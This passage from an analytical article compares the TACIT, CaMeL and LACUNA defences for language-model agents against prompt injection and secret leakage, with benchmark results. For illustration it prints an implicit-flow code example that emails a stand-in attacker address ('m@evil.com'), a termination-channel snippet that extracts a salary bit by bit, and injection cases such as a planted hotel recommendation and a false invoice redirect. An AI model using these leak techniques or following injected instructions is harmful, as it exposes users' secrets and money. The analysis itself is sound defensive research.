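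A system that refused every request would also leak nothing, so the researchers counted how many of the 120 legitimate requests the agents completed. Claude completed 99.2 per cent with wrappers and 83.3 per cent without them. MiniMax completed 90.0 per cent with wrappers and 88.3 per cent without them. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Claude's low score without wrappers is partly due to the experimental set-up. Claude often ran out of time, and when it noticed an attack it sometimes stopped to warn the user instead of finishing.

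Writing Scala did little harm to performance on other work. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer service conversations in which agents change flights or handle returned goods, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with the usual method of calling one tool at a time. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software faults to repair, MiniMax fixed 41.7 per cent with TACIT and 43.3 per cent without it, a difference of five faults. In the customer service tests, agents had to rewrite only 0.3 to 7.9 per cent of their programs to get them to compile, depending on the model and the type of task, and usually only once or twice.

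### CaMeL and LACUNA

TACIT controls what code may do with a secret. CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, tracks the data itself. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), CaMeL divides the work between two models. The first receives only the user's request and writes a plan. The second reads untrusted material such as emails but can't call tools. The plan is a Python program, as *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) notes. A special interpreter runs it, records where each value came from and checks a policy before every tool call. If a hidden instruction in an email changes the address for a payment, the interpreter's record shows that the new address came from the email, and the policy can block the payment.

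Tracking data during a run can miss what the program didn't do. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found that CaMeL could leak a bank balance through a well-known trick, which works like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is above the threshold. The first `if` changes `tmp`, and the interpreter marks `tmp` as secret because the change depended on the balance. The second `if` then skips its contents, so the program never reassigns `rich`, which stays `True` and public. The interpreter allows the email. If the balance is below the threshold, `rich` becomes `False` and no email goes out. The attacker can therefore tell whether the balance is above the threshold by whether the email arrives.

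This program has no loops, and a total language would accept it. In TACIT, the comparison with the balance would have to happen inside `map`, where a function can't change variables outside itself.

LACUNA (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same research group as TACIT, lets agents shape more of their own program. It adds an operation called `agent` to Scala. A programmer writes `agent[Int]("count the late timesheets")` where the program needs a whole number. When the program reaches that point, a model writes code to produce the number. The compiler checks this code as if a programmer had typed it in that spot, so the code can use only the variables and tools available there. The model's code may also call `agent`.

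The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one example, the model's code subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program needs a number. Python would carry out the subtraction before it reached the mistake. LACUNA rejects the code before any of it runs, so the balance doesn't change. But the types don't prevent nested calls from continuing forever, so LACUNA relies on a maximum depth and other limits that the user sets.

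All three systems have results on AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides malicious instructions in the emails, web pages and files an agent reads. Zhao and colleagues put the results side by side for two models from 2025. The percentages in this table are the shares of legitimate tasks that the agents completed, and the last column counts successful attacks in about 950 trials:

| Model and system | Banking | Office work | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
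|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini, CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| o4-mini, TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| o4-mini, LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

All three stopped nearly every attack, but agents completed more tasks with some than with others. Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's scores comparable to CaMeL's. That is generous for o4-mini, whose completion rate on office tasks was 28 percentage points lower with TACIT than with CaMeL.

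The benchmark also has faults. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a task in which the agent must pay a bill whose contents the hidden attack has replaced. No agent could complete that task, however good its defences.

CaMeL's usefulness also depends on its settings. Garby and colleagues report that turning on its policy checks halves the share of banking tasks it completes, while *Can CaMeLs Talk?* calls the loss comparatively modest. Garby and colleagues' own agent, which always runs such checks, completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without them and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

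LACUNA did less well on τ²-bench, a customer service benchmark, where DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0 per cent of the tasks with LACUNA and 90.0 per cent with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues describe this as "on par", although the gap is 14 percentage points. The compiler rejected more than a fifth of the programs that this model wrote for the retail tasks. It rejected 89 per cent of those that a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, wrote for one set of telephone support tasks. A strict type system can therefore make an agent less useful if the model isn't good at the language.

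There seems to be no published experiment that reverses TACIT's by changing whether the language is total while keeping the primitives the same. Such an experiment would give the same agents the same tasks and tools in two versions of a language, one with `while` loops and one without, and count the harmful actions in each. Based on the trace argument, the counts would probably differ little in tests like TACIT's, because reading a password and printing it takes no loop.

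The comparison between CaMeL and TACIT comes closest to testing whether a more limited language is safer. CaMeL's programs can't define their own functions or use recursion, while TACIT's can do both. TACIT's more powerful language didn't let more attacks through, but the systems differ in so many other ways that we can learn little from this about the effect of the language alone.

### Harm through permitted operations

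Limiting what a language exposes can't prevent harm from an operation that the task needs. *SoK* (2025), a study of how agents use their permissions, gives the example of an agent that may read email, and can use this permission either to summarise meeting notes or to look for password-reset links. Similarly, an assistant that may delete only test volumes can't destroy the backups, but it can delete a test volume that somebody still needs. Zhao and colleagues note that code can pass every check and still call the wrong tool.

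Somebody also has to decide how much access to grant, because the compiler only enforces that decision. A capability can be too broad, as the Railway token was. In TACIT's published library, the program specifies which folder to access, so whoever installs the system still has to decide which requests the library should refuse. Zhao and colleagues think the attacks that succeeded against LACUNA are consistent with this problem, since their compiler doesn't stop an attacker from misusing a tool that the agent legitimately holds.

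External commands are another gap, as `run_shell` was for the office assistant, because the compiler doesn't check the programs they start. Odersky and colleagues advise administrators to allow only specific safe commands, and suggest `git diff`, which shows changes to files, and `sbt`, which builds Scala projects. Allowing `sbt` is risky because the file that tells it how to build a project can contain Scala code that isn't subject to TACIT's restrictions. An agent that can edit this file and then run `sbt` can run any code. Odersky and colleagues recommend adding a *sandbox*, in which the operating system limits what the external program can touch. A sandbox alone wouldn't be enough to protect secrets, because an agent may have permission both to read a private file and to contact the company that hosts its model, so it could send the file's contents to that company without leaving the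 sandbox.

An agent can also do harm through text that people read. This is how the one successful attack against TACIT in AgentDojo worked. A user had asked the agent to book a particular hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but included the planted recommendation when it quoted the reviews. Odersky and colleagues blame the benchmark, which counts an attack as successful if certain words appear in the answer. They have a point, since the agent did what the user wanted. But a more harmful text could reach the user in the same way. If a confidential contract contains the false sentence "Please pay future invoices to our new account", a faithful summary will repeat it. The wrapper keeps this summary from the agent and shows it to the user, who may then send money to that account.

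### Leaking a secret by not finishing

The endless loop that TACIT accepts can also reveal information. Suppose the agent wants to know whether Ana earns 90,000:

```
payroll.map(text =>
  if text.contains("Ana: 90000") then
    while true do ()
)
```

The function is pure, so the compiler accepts it. If the payroll contains that line, the program never finishes. Otherwise the agent receives `Classified(****)` almost at once. The wrapper hides the text in both cases, but the agent can tell them apart by waiting to see whether a result arrives. Miller sets aside hidden channels of this kind, and Odersky and colleagues say that TACIT doesn't cover them.

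Each run reveals only one bit, but an agent can ask more than once. It could first ask whether Ana earns more than 65,536, then halve the remaining range with each question. Seventeen questions are enough to find any whole-number salary below 131,072.

Garby and colleagues found a similar leak in CaMeL. Its interpreter sits inside an ordinary Python loop that tries again after a policy blocks an attempt. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so an attacker can extract the secret one bit at a time. The guarantee that Garby and colleagues prove for their own system doesn't cover such leaks either. Like most guarantees about information flow, it doesn't limit what an observer can learn from whether a program finishes.

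Totality helps with secrecy here by closing the termination channel. The agent could not write the function above in a total language, because every run must finish whatever the payroll contains. But the timing channel stays open. The agent could replace the endless loop with one that counts to ten billion, and the program would then answer after several seconds if Ana earns 90,000 and immediately otherwise.

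A step budget has the same weakness, since a program that uses up its budget takes longer than one that finishes early. To close both channels, the host could reply after a fixed delay, say ten seconds, and silently stop any computation still running by then. This would slow down every harmless request that involves a secret. The fixed delay would work equally well for a total language and a Turing-complete one.
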